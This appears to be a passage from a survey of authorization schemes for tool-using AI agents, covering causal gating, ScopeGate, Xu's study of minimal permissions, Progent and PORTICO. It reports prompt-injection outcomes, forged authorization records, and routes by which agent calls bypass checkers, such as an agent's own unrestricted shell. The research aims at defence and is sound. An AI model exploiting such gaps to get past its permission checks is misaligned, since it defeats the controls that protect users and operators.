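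*Beyond OAuth* (2026) proposes PAuth, a system that grants permission for the exact operations a request implies. An OAuth scope might allow transfers in general, whereas PAuth would tie the permission to the details of the transfer the user asked for. This works best when the request is precise. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) notes that it can be unclear how to divide a request into operations, and argues that such systems should be judged by the calls they wrongly refuse and the burden they place on users, as well as by the attacks they prevent.

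Causal gating, the method Iyer and Babu use to hide risky tools, needs even more preparation. Someone has to express the goal as a set of facts, such as `email_sent`, and list what each tool requires and produces. The system then searches for a chain of tools that reaches the goal. It reveals a risky tool only when that tool is the next step in the chain and a trusted source has recorded the necessary authorisation, such as a confirmed recipient.

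In a test with seven models, injected instructions led to a risky call in 25% of trials when the system ignored risk and authorisation, and in none with causal gating. A quarter of the benchmark's tasks contained an unsafe shortcut, which explains the 25% figure. In another test, where the attacker could forge the record of authorisation, the rate with causal gating rose from zero to 25%. The method depends on preventing attackers from forging such records, and it suits tasks whose goals can be defined in advance.

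Researchers also disagree about whether a model should write permissions at all. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) argues that no part of a policy should come from a model's output, even indirectly, because an attack that corrupts a call could also corrupt the rule for checking it. In the paper's system, ScopeGate, a company lists the accounts that may receive payments, and ordinary software refuses payments to any others. An attacking model that learned the reason for each refusal made 29 unauthorised attempts over 40 rounds, and none succeeded.

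This argument is strong for payments to a known set of accounts, where a company can keep the list itself. It is less convincing for a general assistant, because nobody can list every correct recipient, file and website before the user has thought of the task. It also applies less to Progent's first rules, because the model writes them from the user's request before it reads any outside text. The danger is greatest when those rules are later expanded, and Progent requires approval for expansions.

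People make mistakes in policies too. AgentCap includes a program that checks policies before use. In a customer service policy, the program found a tool for deleting customers that no agent could ever use, because the tool required another permission and a second rule prevented the agent from holding both. In a separate test, Santos-Grueiro found that eight templates could reproduce 35 of 36 contract structures, which suggests that people need not write every contract from scratch. Santos-Grueiro did not measure how long the writing takes or whether different authors would agree.

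### Tasks with no smallest permission

Even a complete description of the task may not determine which permission is smallest. *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (Xu, 2026) compares the permissions that Microsoft and Google publish for their online services. For each task, Xu looked for sets of permissions that were sufficient and could not be replaced by another sufficient set allowing strictly fewer operations.

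There are two such solutions for reading information about a project in BigQuery, Google's data-analysis service. One permission covers 286 operations in 10 services, including some that change BigQuery data. The other covers 565 operations in 27 services but is meant only for reading. Neither covers everything the other does. Someone worried about damage would choose the second, while someone worried about leaks might choose the first.

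About 30% to 33% of the tasks for Microsoft Graph, which gives programs access to Microsoft's cloud services, had no single smallest set of permissions. For Google, the figure was 3.2%. "Least privilege" can therefore be ambiguous even when it is clear exactly which operations a task requires. Xu generated the tasks from the companies' own lists of operations, so these figures do not measure how often agents meet the problem in practice.

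MiniScope, a 2025 system, calculates the permissions an agent's plan needs and asks the user to approve them. As Xu describes it, MiniScope works out which OAuth scopes contain others, then uses an optimisation program to choose the set with the lowest cost. If two sets are both minimal, the choice depends on how MiniScope defines cost. Xu recommends showing the alternatives to whoever approves the permission. This would let the user choose between them, though that is harder than answering yes or no.

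Models do not reliably choose permissions well. When Xu asked six leading models to choose among permissions, they picked a minimal one in 99% of 1,708 decisions. But in 22% of the decisions, another option was at least as good on all four of Xu's measures of risk, such as the number of services it reached or the number of operations that could change data. Yu and colleagues also point out that a minimum calculated for the whole task can include permissions the agent does not need yet and others it has finished with.

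### Calls that bypass the checker

All of these systems depend on complete mediation, which means that every action must pass through the checker. Developers cannot assume their tools already provide this. Mellafe Zuvic examined LangChain and LlamaIndex, two frameworks for building agents, and Stripe's tools for agent payments. All three could limit which tools an agent had, but none checked by default whether the values in a call were authorised. A payment to an attacker's account would pass if the account number had the right format.

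Progent can run as a proxy between an existing agent and its MCP servers. This requires no change to the agent's code, but the proxy cannot control tools built into the agent. Developers with access to the agent's code can add Progent inside the agent to control those tools too.

Shell commands are harder to check than ordinary tool calls because one command can read files, change them and contact the network. PORTICO tries to identify these effects before a command runs. If it cannot classify a command, it refuses it or asks for explicit approval. PORTICO can also run as an MCP server, so programmers can use it with existing coding agents. But if such an agent keeps its own unrestricted shell, it can still use it to edit `src/serialization.py` after PORTICO has cancelled its access.
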